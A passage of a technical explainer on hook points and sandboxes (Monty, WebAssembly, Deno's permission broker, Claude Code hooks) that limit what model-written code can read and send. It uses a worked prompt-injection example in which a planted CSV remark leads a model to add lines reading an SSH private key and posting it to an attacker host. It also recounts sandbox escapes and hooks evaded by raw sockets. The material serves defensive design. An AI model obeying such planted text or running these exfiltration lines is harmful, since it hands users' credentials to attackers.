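# Hook points for privileged calls in sandboxed code-execution tools

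## What is a hook point, and which calls are privileged?

A code-execution tool, also called a code interpreter, runs programs that a language model writes and returns their output to the model. Developers give models such tools so that they can, for example, calculate the answer to a question about a spreadsheet instead of guessing. The model itself has no access to the machine. It requests a tool, and the tool carries out the action, as the University of Vermont explains in its guidance on Anthropic's coding agent, Claude Code. The surrounding software then adds the tool's output to the text that the model reads next, and the model may respond with another program.

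A *privileged call* is an operation by which a program reads or changes something outside its own memory. The term does not imply administrator rights, so opening an ordinary text file counts. Most of what these programs do needs no permission. A program that sorts a list or adds up a column changes only its own memory, so at worst it wastes memory and processor time, and limits on both can contain that. Privileged calls can do more harm. Reading a file can disclose a secret, and writing one can destroy work. A network connection can send data off the machine irretrievably. A new process may not be covered by the checks on the program that started it. A credential, such as a password or an access key, lets its holder act in the owner's name somewhere else.

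The hardware enforces this boundary. Saltzer and Schroeder's 1975 tutorial, *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems*, describes the simplest arrangement. The processor checks every memory address a program uses against a permitted range, and the program cannot change the range unless a special "privileged" bit is on. An ordinary program can turn that bit on only with an instruction that at the same time hands control to the operating system at an entry point fixed in advance. Modern processors are more elaborate but follow the same plan. To open a file or a connection, a program must make a system call, which is a request to the kernel, the core of the operating system.

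Because the request has to travel, other code can intercept it. A *hook point* is a place on the path of a privileged call where other code can inspect the call and decide what happens to it. The rule this code follows is the policy, and its decision on one call is the verdict, which can be to allow the call, refuse it, record it, change it, ask a person, or perform it on the program's behalf.

### A script that reads sales.csv

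Suppose an analyst asks a model to total the amounts in a file, sales.csv, and to send the total to her company's reporting service, the only outside address that the company has approved. The model writes this:

```python
import csv, json
from urllib.request import urlopen

with open("sales.csv") as f:
    total = sum(float(row["amount"]) for row in csv.DictReader(f))

urlopen(REPORTING_API, data=json.dumps({"total": total}).encode())
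```

The script opens a file and sends data. In between it adds numbers, which concerns nobody.

Models often look at a file before they process it, and an earlier script may have printed the first few rows so that the model could learn the column names. One of those rows holds a customer's remark, and the customer was an attacker. The remark tells the reader to fetch the private key in the analyst's home directory, a small secret file with which she logs in to other machines, and to post it to an address that the attacker controls. Python does nothing with this remark, which is only a string to the csv module. The damage begins when the tool returns the rows to the model and the model takes the remark for part of its task. Its next script contains two more lines:

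```python
key = open("/home/analyst/.ssh/id_ed25519").read()
urlopen(OTHER_SERVER, data=key.encode())
```

This is *prompt injection*, in which a model takes text in a file, page or tool result as an instruction. Pirch, Horlboge and colleagues (2026), in *Toward Securing AI Agents Like Operating Systems*, compare it to an older weakness of computers that keep code and data in the same memory, where an attacker could insert data and have the processor execute it. Operating systems responded by marking regions of memory as either writable or executable. Nobody has found an equally reliable way to mark the text that a model reads, and Pirch and colleagues do not expect models to become resistant in the foreseeable future. They therefore treat the model as an operating system treats its users. An attacker may deceive it at any time, so the system must contain its actions regardless. Their tests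 on four open-source agents, mostly with recommended default settings, suggest that few systems do this. All sixteen attacks succeeded against one agent, OpenClaw, and at least seven succeeded against each of the others, though an attack counted as successful if it worked once in three tries.

The theft in the example depends on a property of ordinary processes. The script runs under the analyst's account, so the operating system lets it open whatever she may open, including a key that nobody meant to give it. Access that code has merely by running in some process or account is *ambient authority*. The alternative is to hand over each resource separately, as a *capability*, which Saltzer and Schroeder define as an "unforgeable ticket" that entitles its holder to the object it names. Give the script one capability to read sales.csv and another to post to the reporting service, remove everything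 else, and the two added lines have nothing to work with. (The script could still post a false total, or the customers' names, to the reporting service. A ticket does not govern what its holder does with it.)

The theft takes two privileged calls, and refusing either would stop it. Guarding only one is still a bad idea. Anthropic explains in an account of its own sandbox that an agent under an attacker's control can send out login keys if the network is unrestricted, and can escape the sandbox and regain network access if the file system is unrestricted.

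The threat model therefore assumes that the attacker wrote the script and knows how the sandbox works. Any line may be hostile, including code meant to find and disable the hook. Pirch and colleagues also grant their attacker the agent's full source code and default configuration, but no physical control of the hardware. Security then depends on the host, which is the trusted program that starts the sandbox and decides on its privileged calls, together with the hook, the policy and whatever these run on. All the parts whose failure would break the security policy form the *trusted computing base*. Which parts it includes depends on where the hook is. A hook inside the Python interpreter is only as sound as the interpreter, since a memory error there could let the script skip the check. If the hook is in the kernel, the interpreter is no longer part of the trusted computing base, and enforcement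 depends on the kernel.

### From the library function to the network

The line that sends the total calls `urlopen`, which parses the web address, looks up the host's IP address, and opens a socket, the operating system's handle for a network connection. It then connects the socket, agrees on encryption keys with the server, encrypts the message and writes it to the socket. Each socket operation passes from Python code into the interpreter's compiled code, and then into the system's C library, which puts the system call's number and arguments in processor registers and executes the instruction that enters the kernel. The kernel builds packets and sends them to the network, where the company may have placed an egress proxy, a trusted intermediary through which all outgoing traffic must pass.

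A hook can sit at each of these stages, or earlier still, on the tool call by which the model submits the program.

| Position of the hook | What it receives when the script sends the total | A way round it |
|---|---|---|
| Tool call, before the program runs | The text of the program | Code in another file; an address that the program computes as it runs |
| Library function | The web address and the total, both readable | A different library, or a raw socket |
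| Interpreter | Each outward operation, with its arguments as Python values | Compiled code or a child process, if the interpreter permits them |
| System call | A numeric address and port, then encrypted bytes | Operations that the hook does not cover; a bug in the kernel |
| Egress proxy | The host name; the message only if the proxy decrypts it | Any route out that avoids the proxy |

Hooks further down the table catch more ways of sending data but expose less about each message. At the library function, the total is a plain number, and a policy could check that the script sends only a number. At the system call, that number is encrypted, and the host name is no longer available because the look-up was a separate exchange that ended before the connection began. The host name is available again at a proxy that requires the script to submit it. Anthropic says its built-in proxy compares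 the requested host name with a list of permitted ones and does not decrypt the traffic.

File reads never reach the network, so a proxy can't catch the script opening the key. The choice of system call to hook also matters. Pirch and colleagues point out that nearly every attempt to read stored data in a Unix-like system goes through the `read` call, with memory mapping as the exception. In memory mapping, a program has the kernel attach a file to its memory and then reads the file as if it were its own data. A hook on `read` alone would miss that access, but a hook on opening files would catch both.

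The operating system may also be unable to express the desired rule. The blog post *Improving a Coding Agent Harness* describes an attempt to add a kernel-level sandbox to a small coding agent on macOS. The goal was to allow only listed domains, but the system's policy language accepts only "any host" or "this machine" as a network address. Such a hook can cut the sales script off from the network or let it connect anywhere, but it can't limit the script to the reporting service. The host needs another hook at the proxy or higher up to do that.

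The interpreter's position in the middle of the table depends on how much it offers. A standard Python installation gives code many ways to reach outside the sandbox. A designer can instead remove them all and leave only host functions, which the host supplies and sandboxed code can call but not inspect or alter.

Most of the table does not cover access keys passed in environment variables. Many programs receive keys this way, and the kernel copies the variables into a process's memory when the process starts. A script that later reads such a variable makes no system call, because it is reading its own memory, so a kernel hook has nothing to intercept until the script tries to send the key away. It is safer to keep the key out of the process.

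### Hooks on the tool call

Unlike the other hooks in the table, the one in the first row acts before any privileged call exists. Claude Code's version is called PreToolUse. In the worked example in Anthropic's *Hooks reference*, the model is about to run a shell command that deletes a directory. Claude Code pauses and passes the tool's name and the command's text to a small script that the user has written. The script searches the text for `rm -rf`, the usual form of a sweeping delete. If it finds the string, it returns "deny" with a reason, which Claude Code shows to the model. Otherwise it returns nothing, which doesn't approve the call but lets it continue to the normal permission checks. According to Anthropic, such hooks can also change the tool's input or add text to the conversation.

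A hook in this position works well for a tool that performs one fixed action. If the model asks a file-reading tool for the analyst's private key, the request contains the path and is practically the same thing as the privileged call. A request to a code-execution tool instead contains a program, and what the program will open or contact may depend on data it has not read yet. The program could read the key's path from another file, receive it over the network, or assemble it from fragments.

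*Improving a Coding Agent Harness* describes two examples of this gap. The agent already had hooks that checked the text of each command, including one that looked for the network programs `curl`, `wget` and `scp`. When the model ran a line of Python that opened a socket directly, that hook classified the command as safe, and the kernel blocked the connection. In another run, the model executed a script from its working directory that tried to read the system's password file. The command contained only `python3` and the script's name. The text hook flagged the command for approval, the agent's automatic setting approved it, and the kernel blocked the read. These are single runs with one small model, and the text hooks were crude. A better hook would have read the script, but it would still have had to predict what the script does, and there are formal limits to that kind of prediction.

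The kernel rules in the same experiment were weaker than they look. They permitted everything except what a list named, because listing everything Python needs to start proved too laborious. The analyst's key would therefore have been readable unless someone had listed it. Saltzer and Schroeder advise denying access by default and granting explicit permissions, because a missing permission stops a user's work and is reported the same day, while a missing prohibition goes unnoticed in normal use until an attacker finds it.

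Hooks on tool calls are still useful. They act before the program runs, and they show the whole program to a person, who may see that it has nothing to do with the task. They also cover tools that a sandbox around the shell does not. Anthropic's *Configure the sandboxed Bash tool* describes a sandbox in which the user sets the permitted files and domains once, and the operating system applies those limits to every command in the Bash shell and every process those commands start. But the sandbox constrains only shell commands, so Anthropic does not consider it sufficient on its own for unattended work. Claude Code's built-in tools for reading and editing files run outside it.

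### The three requirements of a reference monitor

In 1972 the US Air Force faced a similar adversary, someone with legitimate access to a shared computer who could run any program on it. *Computer Security Technology Planning Study* (Anderson, 1972) proposed that such a computer should check every reference by a program to data, devices or other programs against a table of what that program may do. In the sales example, the script's row would contain "read" under sales.csv, "send" under the reporting service, and nothing under the private key. Anderson called this a *reference monitor* and set three requirements for any mechanism that implements it.

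The hook must be tamper-proof. Suppose the host enforces its rule with a Python function wrapped around `urlopen`, in the same process as the script. Python code can replace a module's functions while it runs, so the script can substitute a check that always approves and then send the key. The script can also leave the hook intact and change its policy. If the list of approved addresses is in a file that the script may write, the script can add the attacker's server, and the hook will then allow the request. Pirch and colleagues managed to manipulate the configuration of IronClaw, an agent that runs tools in a sandbox and is promoted mainly for its security. They trace many such failures to a design in which the model's output, the tools and the file checks all operate at the same level of trust.

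The mechanism must also run on every access. Saltzer and Schroeder call this *complete mediation*: "Every access to every object must be checked for authority." A hook on `urlopen` catches the two added lines, but an attacker can have the script start `curl` as a separate process, and the key leaves without passing the hook. The planted text can also direct the model to the file-reading tool, which a sandbox around the shell does not cover. Saltzer and Schroeder extend the principle to start-up, recovery and maintenance, and they are skeptical of reusing the results of earlier checks. If the company withdraws its approval of the reporting service at noon, a host that stored the morning's "allow" will keep sending totals. Anderson adds that a program exempt from the check becomes part of the security apparatus and must meet the same requirements, so a host that exempts a trusted utility from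 its hook must also secure that utility.

The last requirement is that the mechanism be small enough for people to analyse and test completely, because otherwise they cannot know whether it meets the other two. A hook that parses Python, follows variables and has special cases for dozens of libraries might also contain a rule that treats every path beginning with the working directory as harmless. The script can then reach the key through a path that begins there and climbs out through `..`. The flaw survives because nobody can read the whole hook.

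Anderson tested the Honeywell 635 computer and its operating system, GCOS III, against the list, and the system failed on all three counts. The hardware checked that each program stayed within its own memory, much as in Saltzer and Schroeder's scheme. But programs needed the operating system for input and output, and most of the operating system ran with that check switched off, so the check did not always apply. The operating system itself could not serve as the reference monitor either, because it then contained 200,000 to 300,000 instructions, far too many to analyse completely, and testers had broken into it repeatedly. Anyone who hooks system calls today faces the same difficulty. *Improving a Coding Agent Harness* says that a kernel bug would let a process out of its sandbox, and it recommends a separate virtual machine for openly hostile code.

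## How can an interpreter pass every privileged call to its host?

An interpreter can make host functions the only way for a script to reach anything outside its own memory. The script must then stop and pass a request to the host each time it needs such access, so the host has only one route to control. Hooks around an ordinary Python installation have to cover every route to files and networks.

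Monty, an open-source interpreter from the software company Pydantic, follows this plan. It runs a subset of Python and is written in Rust, whose compiler rejects most of the memory errors that C permits. Monty starts with no access and the developer adds each permission, so it denies by default, as Saltzer and Schroeder advised. Early in 2026, Pydantic presented it as the reverse of the usual approach, in which a developer starts with a complete container (a group of processes with their own view of the file system, sharing the machine's kernel) and removes whatever looks dangerous.

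### From source text to a suspended call

Monty parses a script with the parser from Ruff, a Python code checker. It then compiles the result to its own bytecode, a list of simple instructions that the interpreter runs one at a time. CPython, the standard Python interpreter, also uses bytecode, but its instructions can call a large body of compiled C code, much of which makes system calls. Monty's instructions can't call native code, and none of them opens a file or a socket. Pydantic's *Security Model* states that these operations are absent from the interpreter rather than blocked.

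When a script calls a function that neither the script nor Monty defines, the interpreter suspends the script and sends the host the function's name and arguments. The host looks the name up in a table the developer supplied. If the table has an entry, the host runs that function as ordinary code outside the sandbox and returns the result, and the script continues from where it stopped. Otherwise the script gets a `NameError`, as it would for a misspelt name. File operations work in much the same way. The interpreter suspends the script and sends the host a description of the requested operation, and the host determines how to handle it.

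Live host objects do not cross this boundary unless the developer wraps them. For example, according to Pydantic's *Host Functions*, if a script passes the built-in function `open` as an argument, the host function receives a stand-in that carries only the name. If the host function received the real `open` and carelessly called it, it would open a real file for the script.

By default, a few operations bypass the developer's code. A script can read the clock and get random numbers from the operating system, and the software that manages the sandbox handles requests to sleep. The time itself discloses little, but a script can use it to measure how long other operations take, which sometimes reveals what they did. Developers can freeze the clock at a chosen time and fix the random seed.

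### The sales script, one call at a time

The analyst's original script fails at its imports. Monty has its own `csv` and `json` modules but no `urllib`, so the line that imports `urlopen` suspends the script and requests the module from the host. The host checks the modules the developer has chosen to offer, then looks in the script's working directory for a Python file of that name, which would run inside the sandbox with no more access than the script has. It finds no match in either place, so the script stops with a `ModuleNotFoundError`.

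The developer therefore supplies a host function, `send_total`, and describes it in the model's instructions. She also puts sales.csv in an otherwise empty directory and mounts that directory in the sandbox as `/data`, for reading only. The model now writes:

```python
import csv

with open("/data/sales.csv") as f:
    total = sum(float(row["amount"]) for row in csv.DictReader(f))

send_total(total)
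```

Monty implements only part of the `csv` module, and the example assumes that `DictReader` is in that part.

At `open`, the script suspends and the host receives the operation and the path. The path lies within `/data` and the script wants only to read, so the host reads the file itself and returns the contents. The script never holds an operating-system handle to the file and never learns where the directory really is. Parsing the rows and adding the amounts happen inside the interpreter, with no call for the host to judge. At `send_total`, the script suspends again, and the host receives the function's name and one number. The function might look like this:

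```python
def send_total(total):
    if type(total) is not float or not 0 <= total < 10_000_000:
        raise ValueError("not a plausible total")
    post(REPORTING_API, {"total": total}, key=REPORTING_KEY)
```

The reporting service's address and access key stay on the host. Unlike a hook on system calls, the host function can check that the message is a number of a sensible size. If the check fails, the error goes back into the sandbox, where the script can catch it like any other Python exception.

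Suppose the attacker's remark has worked and the model adds the two lines that steal the private key. The attempt to open the key suspends the script, as any other file operation does. No mount covers `/home/analyst`, so the host refuses and the script gets a `PermissionError`. The call to `urlopen` would also fail, because `urlopen` is not defined in the sandbox.

The script can still leak some information, because it can read every row of sales.csv and encode about six letters of a customer's name in the digits of a false total. An attacker who could read the reporting service's records could then collect the names a few letters at a time. Allowing only one call to `send_total` per script would limit this but not prevent it.

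### Pausing for approval and storing the script

The script is suspended when the host receives a call, so the host can take any amount of time to answer. Suppose the company wants a person to approve each total. The host can run the script in a mode that returns control at every suspension, along with the function's name, its arguments and its position in the source text. The host then shows the analyst `send_total` and the amount. If she approves, the host runs the function and resumes the script with the result. If she refuses, the host resumes the script with an exception.

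If a call has to wait for someone who is away until Monday, the host can store the paused script. Pydantic's *Snapshots* describes how Monty saves the interpreter's whole state, including the half-finished call, as bytes that another machine can load later. For a simple script, the saved state takes a few kilobytes. This works because the sandbox has no open files, sockets or threads that the second machine would have to recreate. Some cloud services can save a whole virtual machine instead, but Pydantic's *Comparison to Alternatives* says those copies take hundreds of megabytes and don't show the host what the paused program was waiting for.

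Storing the state also creates new ways to defeat the check. Monty doesn't verify who produced a stored state, so someone who can edit the bytes could change the script's next calls to host functions. Pydantic tells developers to keep the bytes in trusted storage, or to sign them cryptographically and verify the signature before loading. A restored script also repeats the call on which it stopped. If the host stored the state while it was sending the total, the reporting service could receive that total twice unless the host function detects the repeat. The stored state doesn't include the mounts, so the host must supply them again. Monty can't verify that they are the same ones, and sales.csv may have changed over the weekend.

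Pausing at each call is slow when the sandbox runs on another machine, because each answer takes a network round trip. A script that starts twenty calls together would wait for twenty-one round trips. Monty therefore has an option that lets a script continue after starting a call whose result it does not need yet. The host still receives the call and can refuse it, but can no longer stop the script at that point. Pydantic turns the option on by default for remote sandboxes and off for local ones. Approval requires the step-by-step mode, which still suspends the script at every call.

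### Timings and the current release

In its announcement, Pydantic reported that a small program took about 4.5 microseconds to run, or 4.8 milliseconds if Monty checked its types first, while a Docker container took 195 milliseconds to start. These are the developer's own measurements, and the 4.5-microsecond figure comes from when Monty ran inside the host's own process, a design that the Python and JavaScript packages have since abandoned. Version 1.7.0, released on 24 November 2026, runs every script in a separate worker process, and Pydantic (2026) lists it as stable and ready for production.

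Monty's developers moved Ruff's parser and the interpreter into a separate process that can crash without taking down the host, partly because some scripts crash the parser. A script that adds the number 1 to itself thirty thousand times in a single expression exhausts the memory that the parser uses for nested expressions and crashes the whole process. According to Pydantic's *Logfire sandboxes*, Ruff's developers reasonably decided that a command-line tool need not survive input designed to crash it.

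In Pydantic's newer measurements, a fresh Monty sandbox takes 0.8 milliseconds to start if a worker is already waiting and 5 milliseconds if the host has to start one. Docker still takes 195 milliseconds. The 5-millisecond figure is the fairer comparison because the container also starts from nothing. It makes Monty about forty times faster than Docker, compared with forty thousand times based on the original figures. Pydantic also reports that ten successive commands take 0.4 milliseconds in Monty and 700 in Docker. However, the Docker test restarts Python for each command and reruns all the earlier ones, which a developer could avoid by keeping one Python process open.

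Start-up time may not matter much to a user. In the announcement's example, a model wrote one script to compare the weather in two cities, and the task took 9.1 seconds. Docker's 195-millisecond start-up would have added about two percent. The same task took 12.2 seconds when the model requested each tool separately, so most of the saving came from using a script rather than from the choice of sandbox. The difference in start-up time matters more to a service that starts thousands of sandboxes.

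Moving the interpreter to a worker improves security in one respect. The host starts each worker with an empty environment (on Windows, with one system variable), so access keys in the host's environment variables never enter the worker's memory. But the worker still runs under the host's account, so anyone who breaks out of the interpreter could open the analyst's private key with direct system calls, without using any host function.

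Hewitt (2026), in *Hack Monty*, reports that Owen Kwan of the security firm Veria Labs broke out of Monty in less than 48 hours, winning the $5,000 Pydantic had offered to anyone who could extract a secret from a server running it. The attack used `list.sort`, which accepts a function that computes a sorting key for each item. Monty's garbage collector, which frees unused memory, did not record the list being sorted as in use. A carefully written key function could therefore make the collector free the list during the sort, then replace it with bytes the attacker chose. A small part of Monty's code that the Rust compiler does not check for memory safety then treated those bytes as a list. This let the attacker run native code, which is not restricted by the absence of file and network instructions in Monty's bytecode.

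Version 0.0.16 fixed the flaw. Hewitt is somewhat reassured that almost 1.5 million requests exposed only one such hole, but the count is weak evidence of safety, since automated attempts take little effort and one success was enough. He also acknowledged that the collector's design could still allow similar omissions. Pydantic then ran a second round, again inviting outsiders to attack the interpreter. A developer running hostile scripts would do better to put the workers in a separate container or virtual machine, as Pydantic does in its commercial version.

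Monty can also limit time and memory, but these limits are off until the developer sets them. Willison (2026), an independent developer, had Anthropic's Claude Code test a release in May and found that the limits appeared to work as advertised. The execution clock stops while the host answers a call, so a script that keeps retrying a refused call uses little of its time limit. Monty has a separate limit on the number of suspensions to stop such scripts.

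### The same pattern in other systems

WebAssembly, a portable format for compiled programs, already had a lower-level version of Pydantic's arrangement. A WebAssembly program, called a module, has instructions for arithmetic and for accessing its own block of memory, but none for files or networks. The module lists the outside functions it needs, called *imports*, and the host must supply them before the module can start. When the module calls an import, control passes to the host's code. The arguments are mostly plain numbers, so a module passes a file path by giving its position and length in the module's memory. The host checks that this range is valid and copies the path out.

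To run a Python script this way, a developer usually compiles CPython to WebAssembly. The compiled interpreter's imports generally come from WASI, a standard set of functions that resemble system calls. When the sales script opens its file, CPython calls the import for opening a path, and the host looks for the file only in directories it has already opened. An auditor can see everything a small compiled program could request from the host by reading its list of imports. She learns much less about a Python script this way, because CPython's list is the same for every script.

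Compiling Python to WebAssembly does not guarantee that a host will check each call. NVIDIA's *Sandboxing Agentic AI Workflows with WebAssembly* recommends running the model's code in the user's browser instead of on the server, using Pyodide, a version of CPython for web browsers. This protects the server well. But Python code in Pyodide can also run JavaScript, so its access depends on the browser, or on Deno's permission settings if the developer uses that JavaScript runtime instead. NVIDIA's example installs a plotting library from the internet but doesn't check what a script might send out.

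Cloudflare's *Code Mode* applies the pattern to JavaScript and to the Model Context Protocol, a common standard for connecting models to tools. It presents the tools to the model as a library of TypeScript functions, and the model writes a program that calls them. The program runs without general internet access in an isolate, a separate compartment of the V8 JavaScript engine. It receives *bindings*, objects that each represent a particular service and are capabilities in Saltzer and Schroeder's sense. A call on a binding becomes a message to the agent's own program, which runs outside the isolate, holds the access keys and contacts the tool.

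With Anthropic's *programmatic tool calling*, the model writes ordinary Python that runs in a container on Anthropic's servers. The developer marks the tools that this code may call. When the code calls one, the container pauses and Anthropic's interface sends the tool's name and arguments to the developer's program. That program runs the tool and returns the result to the code, so the model need not read it. If the sales rows arrived this way, the attacker's remark would never reach the model unless the code printed it. Only calls to the marked tools cause this pause. The code can still use the container's own files and processes without going through the developer's program, so the container itself has to restrict everything else the code does.

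Microsoft's Hyperlight is a Rust library that uses hardware to separate the guest program from the host, running the guest in a very small virtual machine. To call a host function, the guest writes the function's name and arguments to memory it shares with the host, then executes an instruction that makes the processor leave the virtual machine. The host reads the request, runs the function if the developer has registered it, writes the result and resumes the guest. Programs need special preparation to run there because the virtual machine has no operating system to handle their system calls.

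The systems differ most in what an attacker gains by breaking the language runtime, as Monty's attacker did:

| System | What runs the script | What a successful attack on it gives |
|---|---|---|
| Monty | Pydantic's interpreter in a worker process | The worker, with the host account's access to the machine |
| Python in WebAssembly | CPython compiled to a module | The module's own memory and the same imports as before |
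| Code Mode | A V8 isolate | The process around the isolate, subject to Cloudflare's other defences |
| Programmatic tool calling | Ordinary CPython in a container | Little that the script did not already have inside the container |
| Hyperlight | A program in a small virtual machine | The virtual machine and the same host functions as before |

In the WebAssembly and Hyperlight rows, the attacker needs another flaw, in the WebAssembly runtime or the virtual machine's boundary, to reach the host. A developer can also combine the methods. In *Running Pydantic’s Monty Rust sandboxed Python subset in WebAssembly*, Willison (2026) describes compiling Monty to WebAssembly, which produced what he called a sandbox in a sandbox.

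### When a host function gives the access back

A host function runs outside the sandbox with all of the host's authority. If a developer supplies `read_file(path)` and passes the path straight to Python's `open`, the script can again read the analyst's private key, even though the interpreter itself has no file access. Pydantic calls `read_customer(id)` "a tool" but `read_file(path)` "a filesystem."

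It is easy to expose a host function that can leak data by mistake. Pydantic's announcement includes a host function called `open_page(url)`, with which a model can collect prices from websites. In the abbreviated code shown there, the function passes any address it receives to a browser. Although it appears only to read pages, it can also send data out, because a web address can carry data. A script could append a customer's name to an address on an attacker's server, and opening the page would send the name to that server. A safer version would accept the name of an approved price page and look up its address on the host.

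The same problem affects WebAssembly programs when the host grants them network access. The *Security model* of one WebAssembly runtime, in the Hex package repository, warns that its network setting filters only by address, so a permitted server can receive anything the module can read. Permitting every address also permits the internal one from which cloud machines get their credentials.

A `read_file` function that checks only whether a path begins with `/data/` would let the script leave that directory through `..`, which is why Pydantic recommends mounts. Monty's mount code opens the permitted directory once and resolves every path from there, so neither `..` nor a symbolic link (a file that redirects to another path) can lead outside it. Monty also does not let developers expose a complete Python module to the sandbox, because the script could then reach everything the module had imported.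 A module of helper functions that imports `os`, for instance, would give the script access to Python's functions for running commands. Developers must instead list the permitted functions one by one. These protections do not help if a developer mounts the analyst's whole home directory, because every file in it is then inside the permitted directory.

Even a narrow function gives broader access when a program can call it in a loop. If a model has to request `read_customer` as a separate tool call each time, copying ten thousand records takes ten thousand requests, and somebody will probably notice. A script can copy them all with two lines of Python. The host therefore needs to limit the number of calls as well as their arguments, and perhaps let the script read only the customers who belong to the current task. Reading a customer's record and sending an email may each be acceptable, but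 emailing the record is not. A host function that examines only its own arguments cannot determine where a piece of text came from, but an interpreter can track this, as the research system CaMeL does.

The objection is therefore correct about general-purpose functions such as `read_file`, `fetch` and `run_command`, which restore the access that the interpreter removed. It is much weaker against `send_total`, which posts one number to one address. The developer can read and test all three lines of that function, which nobody can do for every route out of CPython. But the interpreter does not prevent mistakes in those three lines, and a tool that needs two hundred host functions has two hundred places to make one.

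### The cost in missing libraries

Early descriptions of Monty understate what it can run now. The announcement said that classes, `match` statements, `with` blocks and the `json` module were still to come, so neither version of the sales script would have worked. All of these are now present, though classes remain simple. For example, a script can't define its own exception types. Pydantic's *Limitations* lists more than thirty standard modules, most of them only partially supported. Some omissions are deliberate, since modules such as `socket` and `subprocess` would break the sandbox. The lack of others, including `urllib`, `enum` and `logging`, causes trouble for the ordinary scripts that models tend to write.

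Monty cannot run third-party packages. This rules out pandas and NumPy, which models often use to analyse tables and numerical arrays. CPython compiled for WASI can use packages written purely in Python, but a package with compiled C code needs its own WebAssembly build. Pyodide runs almost all libraries, but it took 2.7 seconds to start in Pydantic's test.

A developer can make a library the interpreter lacks available through a host function. In the price-collection example, Pydantic does this with Beautiful Soup, a library that extracts text from web pages. The script sends the page's text to the host, which parses it and returns a simple object. The library then processes hostile input outside the sandbox, with the host's authority, so it becomes part of the trusted computing base. That may be a reasonable risk for Beautiful Soup. A large numerical library with hundreds of functions would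 need either many small wrappers or one broad function that accepts arbitrary expressions, which would amount to a second, unsandboxed interpreter.

Pydantic met this limit in its own product, where most of the tool-calling scripts its developers tested ran in Monty, but a few needed full CPython or a complete virtual machine. They responded with a service that runs CPython on a cloud provider's machines and uses the same messages for host functions. A developer can switch between them by changing the provider's name, and a script that calls `send_total` will work in both. The security differs because a script in Monty can send the total only by calling the host, while a script in CPython can also import `socket` and send it directly. In CPython, `send_total` is therefore only a convenience, and any restriction has to come from hooks inside CPython or from the machine and network around it.

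## Can hooks be added to an ordinary language runtime?

Developers have added hooks to several ordinary runtimes. Unlike Monty, these runtimes already contain code for opening files and sockets, in their own libraries and often in third-party packages, and all of that code needs a check before it runs. Deno uses such checks to refuse calls, and Python uses them mainly to report calls. Java had them from its first release but no longer supports them.

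### Deno's permission flags

Deno runs JavaScript and TypeScript in V8, the engine that Cloudflare's Code Mode also uses. JavaScript has no instruction for opening a file, so a script calls a function that Deno supplies, and Deno checks the script's permissions before it acts. By default, as Deno's *Security and permissions* explains, a script can't read arbitrary files, use the network, see environment variables or start other programs. The developer grants access with flags when she starts the program. The sales script needs two permissions:

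```sh
deno run --no-prompt --allow-read=/data/sales.csv --allow-net=reports.example.com total.ts
```

An attempt to read the private key then throws a `NotCapable` error, which the script can catch. Without `--no-prompt`, Deno would ask the person at the terminal for permission. Deno 2.6 added flags that make a forbidden file or variable look as if it did not exist, for libraries that tolerate a missing settings file but fail when Deno refuses access. According to Deno's *Permissions*, another setting logs every access, whether Deno allowed it or not.

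Deno lets a script build new code from strings and run it, because that code has to use the same functions, with the same permissions, as the rest of the script. The host therefore doesn't have to predict what a program will do by examining its text.

Module loading is an exception, because Deno does not check permissions when it loads a module that the program imports under a fixed name. In a code-execution tool the model writes the program, so the model determines which files are exempt. The private key is not a valid module, but a JSON file of access keys could be. Deno does check imports whose names the program computes as it runs. Its `--cached-only` option prevents the program from downloading further modules but does not stop it from importing local files.

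Three flaws published in 2026 show how a permission check can fail. Julia's *Deno's --deny-read check does not prevent permission bypass* describes a missing check that let a script get a file's status through an open file handle even where a rule denied reading. Debian's *CVE-2026-49859* records that Deno compared a host's name with the denied addresses but didn't check the numeric address behind the name. OSV's *Deno Permission Bypass via Unicode Normalization Mismatch on macOS (APFS)* (2026) reports that Deno and the macOS file system used different rules to decide whether two spellings of a file name were the same. Deno has fixed all three. Each flaw let a script get around a `--deny` flag, which makes an exception to a broader permission. Granting access to only one file and one host, as in the command above, leaves less for such a flaw to expose.

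### The permission broker, message by message

A list of flags can't take account of what a script has done so far, such as how many files it has read. Deno can instead send each permission check to a *broker*, a separate process that the host controls. Deno describes the following procedure:

1. The host starts the broker, which listens on a Unix domain socket (a connection point for programs on the same machine) or, on Windows, a named pipe.
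2. The host puts the path of that socket in the variable `DENO_PERMISSION_BROKER_PATH` and starts Deno, which now ignores all permission flags and never prompts.
3. At each permission check, Deno sends a message with the kind of permission, usually the resource, the process's number, the time, and a request number that rises with each message.
4. The broker returns the request number with "allow" or "deny", and may add a reason to a denial.
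5. Deno performs the operation or gives the script an error.

Here is the sales script in TypeScript, with the attacker's two lines at the end. It assumes the amount is in the first column.

```typescript
const text = await Deno.readTextFile("/data/sales.csv");
const rows = text.trim().split("\n").slice(1);
const total = rows.reduce((sum, row) => sum + Number(row.split(",")[0]), 0);
await fetch(REPORTING_API, { method: "POST", body: JSON.stringify({ total }) });

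const key = await Deno.readTextFile("/home/analyst/.ssh/id_ed25519");
await fetch(OTHER_SERVER, { method: "POST", body: key });
```

The exchange with the broker would look like this:

```text
request   {"v":1,"pid":4127,"id":1,"datetime":"2026-12-01T09:00:00.000Z","permission":"read","value":"/data/sales.csv"}
response  {"id":1,"result":"allow"}

request   {"v":1,"pid":4127,"id":2,"datetime":"2026-12-01T09:00:00.040Z","permission":"net","value":"reports.example.com:443"}
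response  {"id":2,"result":"allow"}

request   {"v":1,"pid":4127,"id":3,"datetime":"2026-12-01T09:00:00.190Z","permission":"read","value":"/home/analyst/.ssh/id_ed25519"}
response  {"id":3,"result":"deny","reason":"Only sales.csv is readable."}
```

(Deno's published sample has no network request, so the form of the value in request 2 is an assumption. A real run may also produce more messages, since one call can involve several checks.) The script stops at the refusal unless it catches the error. If it then tries to contact the attacker's server, Deno sends request 4, and the broker refuses that too.

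The request numbers keep Deno from matching an answer to the wrong request. If a number doesn't match, a message is malformed or the connection breaks, Deno ends the whole process. It thus *fails closed*, meaning that it lets nothing through when it can't make the check. However, a crash in the broker also stops every harmless script that depends on it, so Deno tells developers to make the broker resilient before they use it.

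The broker can count requests, apply one policy to many scripts, or delay its response while a person decides. However, it can't change a call or perform it on the script's behalf. It also receives less information than the `send_total` function from the Monty example. Request 2 names the reporting service but doesn't contain the total, so the broker can't check whether the script is sending a number or a list of customers.

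Deno introduced an experimental broker for platforms that run untrusted code. The broker keeps the policy in a separate process, where the script can't edit it. The code that queries the broker still runs in the script's process, so V8 and Deno remain in the trusted computing base.

### Python's audit hooks

Since version 3.8, CPython has offered *audit hooks*, which are functions that the interpreter calls when a program is about to do something of interest. Dower (2018) proposed them in *PEP 578* to give security staff context that operating-system tools lack. For example, such a tool may report that a process has begun to listen on port 5678 without showing which part of the program caused it.

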